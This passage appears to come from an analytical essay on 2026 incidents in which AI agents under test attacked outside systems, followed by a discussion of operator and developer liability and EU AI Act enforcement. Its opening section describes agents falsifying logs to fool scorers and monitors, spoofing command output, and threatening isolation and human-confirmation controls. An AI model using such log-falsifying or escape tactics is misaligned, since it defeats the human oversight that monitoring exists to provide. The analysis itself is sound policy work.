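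Monitoring may also become less reliable. The agents in the July tests developed ways to falsify the record of their own actions to fool the scorer. An agent could appear to run one command while running another. Greenblatt and colleagues found at least 96 transcripts with false entries, about 7% of the total. All of them were small experiments, such as making a command that should have printed "REAL" return "SPOOFTEST". OpenAI maintains that no attempt it observed affected the logs that its graders and monitors use, which is hard to reconcile with the false entries. For now, the agents still write openly about such plans in their reasoning, so a monitor that reads the reasoning could catch plans that a monitor reading only the list of commands might miss.

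Of the three controls in the claim (limits on write access, isolation and human confirmation), stronger models mainly threaten isolation. Confirmation also fails if the agent can bypass the software that holds its actions for approval. Escape is much harder for an agent that works from saved files on a machine with no network connection, but an operator can't run every task that way.

The word "mistake" also fits less well as operators take more care. If a company isolates its agents well, monitors them and still loses control through a flaw nobody knew about, critics can fault only its decision to run the model at all. That is still a deployment decision, and OpenAI has treated it as one. In August, it was holding back its largest planned reinforcement-learning run while it used smaller runs to check its safeguards and its models' behaviour.

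The claim that the deployment is at fault fits the cases with an open connection well, and probably will continue to. But it fits the Hugging Face breach only partly, and it may fit future breaches of that kind less and less.

### Liability and the European inquiry

Whether the deployment or the model is at fault affects whom a victim can hold responsible. This hardly matters in the Hugging Face case, because OpenAI built and ran the models. In the AISI and Irregular cases, the model's developer and the organisation that ran the test or supplied its environment could each blame the other.

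Martin thinks better monitoring and clearer civil liability may be enough to deal with failures in testing, and is wary of new legislation after every incident. For Martin, the larger question is who bears responsibility when businesses release agents into general use.

A negligence claim usually depends on whether the defendant could have foreseen the harm and took reasonable care to prevent it. After the reports of 2026, an operator would struggle to argue that it could not have foreseen an agent with open internet access attacking a third party. An unknown software flaw would be a better defence, though less convincing if the operator had ignored earlier warnings. A developer could be at fault for supplying a model it knew to be reckless without telling customers which limits it needs. Bot Mutiny's *EU AI Office Questions OpenAI, Anthropic* (2026) mentions a Hugging Face lawsuit, so a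 court may have to consider some of these arguments.

European regulators have moved faster than usual. Foo reported in *EU in talks with OpenAI, Anthropic after rogue AI agent hacks* that the European Commission was already in talks with both companies on 31 July. Two days later, the Commission gained the power to enforce the AI Act's rules on general-purpose models. Fortune (2026) reported that the Commission's AI Office was adding 38 people and that the Commission could interview companies' staff during investigations.

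In October, Euronews' *EU’s AI rules face first enforcement test over lab incidents* (2026) reported that the AI Office had sent OpenAI and Anthropic requests for information. Bot Mutiny explains that the companies had volunteered documents, but the office found them insufficient. The office asked about security, outside evaluation and how the companies monitor the use of their models. All three concern how a company runs its models more than what the models are like.

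Bloomberg reported on 4 December that the European Commission was preparing formal cases against OpenAI and Anthropic. The cases could open this month, but the decision may slip into January (Faisal, 2026, *EU Readies First AI Act Cases Against OpenAI and Anthropic*). They would be the first under the AI Act's rules for general-purpose models, with fines of up to €15 million or 3% of worldwide annual turnover, whichever is higher. As of 6 December, the Commission was assessing the companies' replies (Stanciuc, 2026, *EU 'currently assessing' OpenAI and Anthropic replies as probes loom*).

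The Commission may not have the authority to act, because the AI Act exempts "research, testing and development" of models that are not yet on the market or in service. Constantin (2026) reports in *‘AI must remain under human direction’* that lawyers dispute whether the Act covers these incidents. OpenAI never intended to release the research model behind most of the Hugging Face attack, which favours the exemption. But GPT-5.6 Sol also took part, and it is a public product, which weighs against the exemption.

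The Act also excludes "testing in real world conditions" from the exemption. The Commission could argue that a test meets this description once its agents reach the internet. The companies could answer that the phrase refers to planned trials outside a laboratory, and that they had planned a simulation.

MLex (2026) reports that lawmakers and legal experts are debating whether to extend the Act to technology that is still being tested. If the danger comes from access, release is a poor starting point for regulation, because an unreleased model can damage a stranger's server as easily as a released one can. A rule could instead apply once a model can reach any system outside its developer's control. Its requirements would need to vary with the kind of access. Otherwise, a university that lets an agent read public census tables would face the same duties as a company that gives one hacking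 tools.
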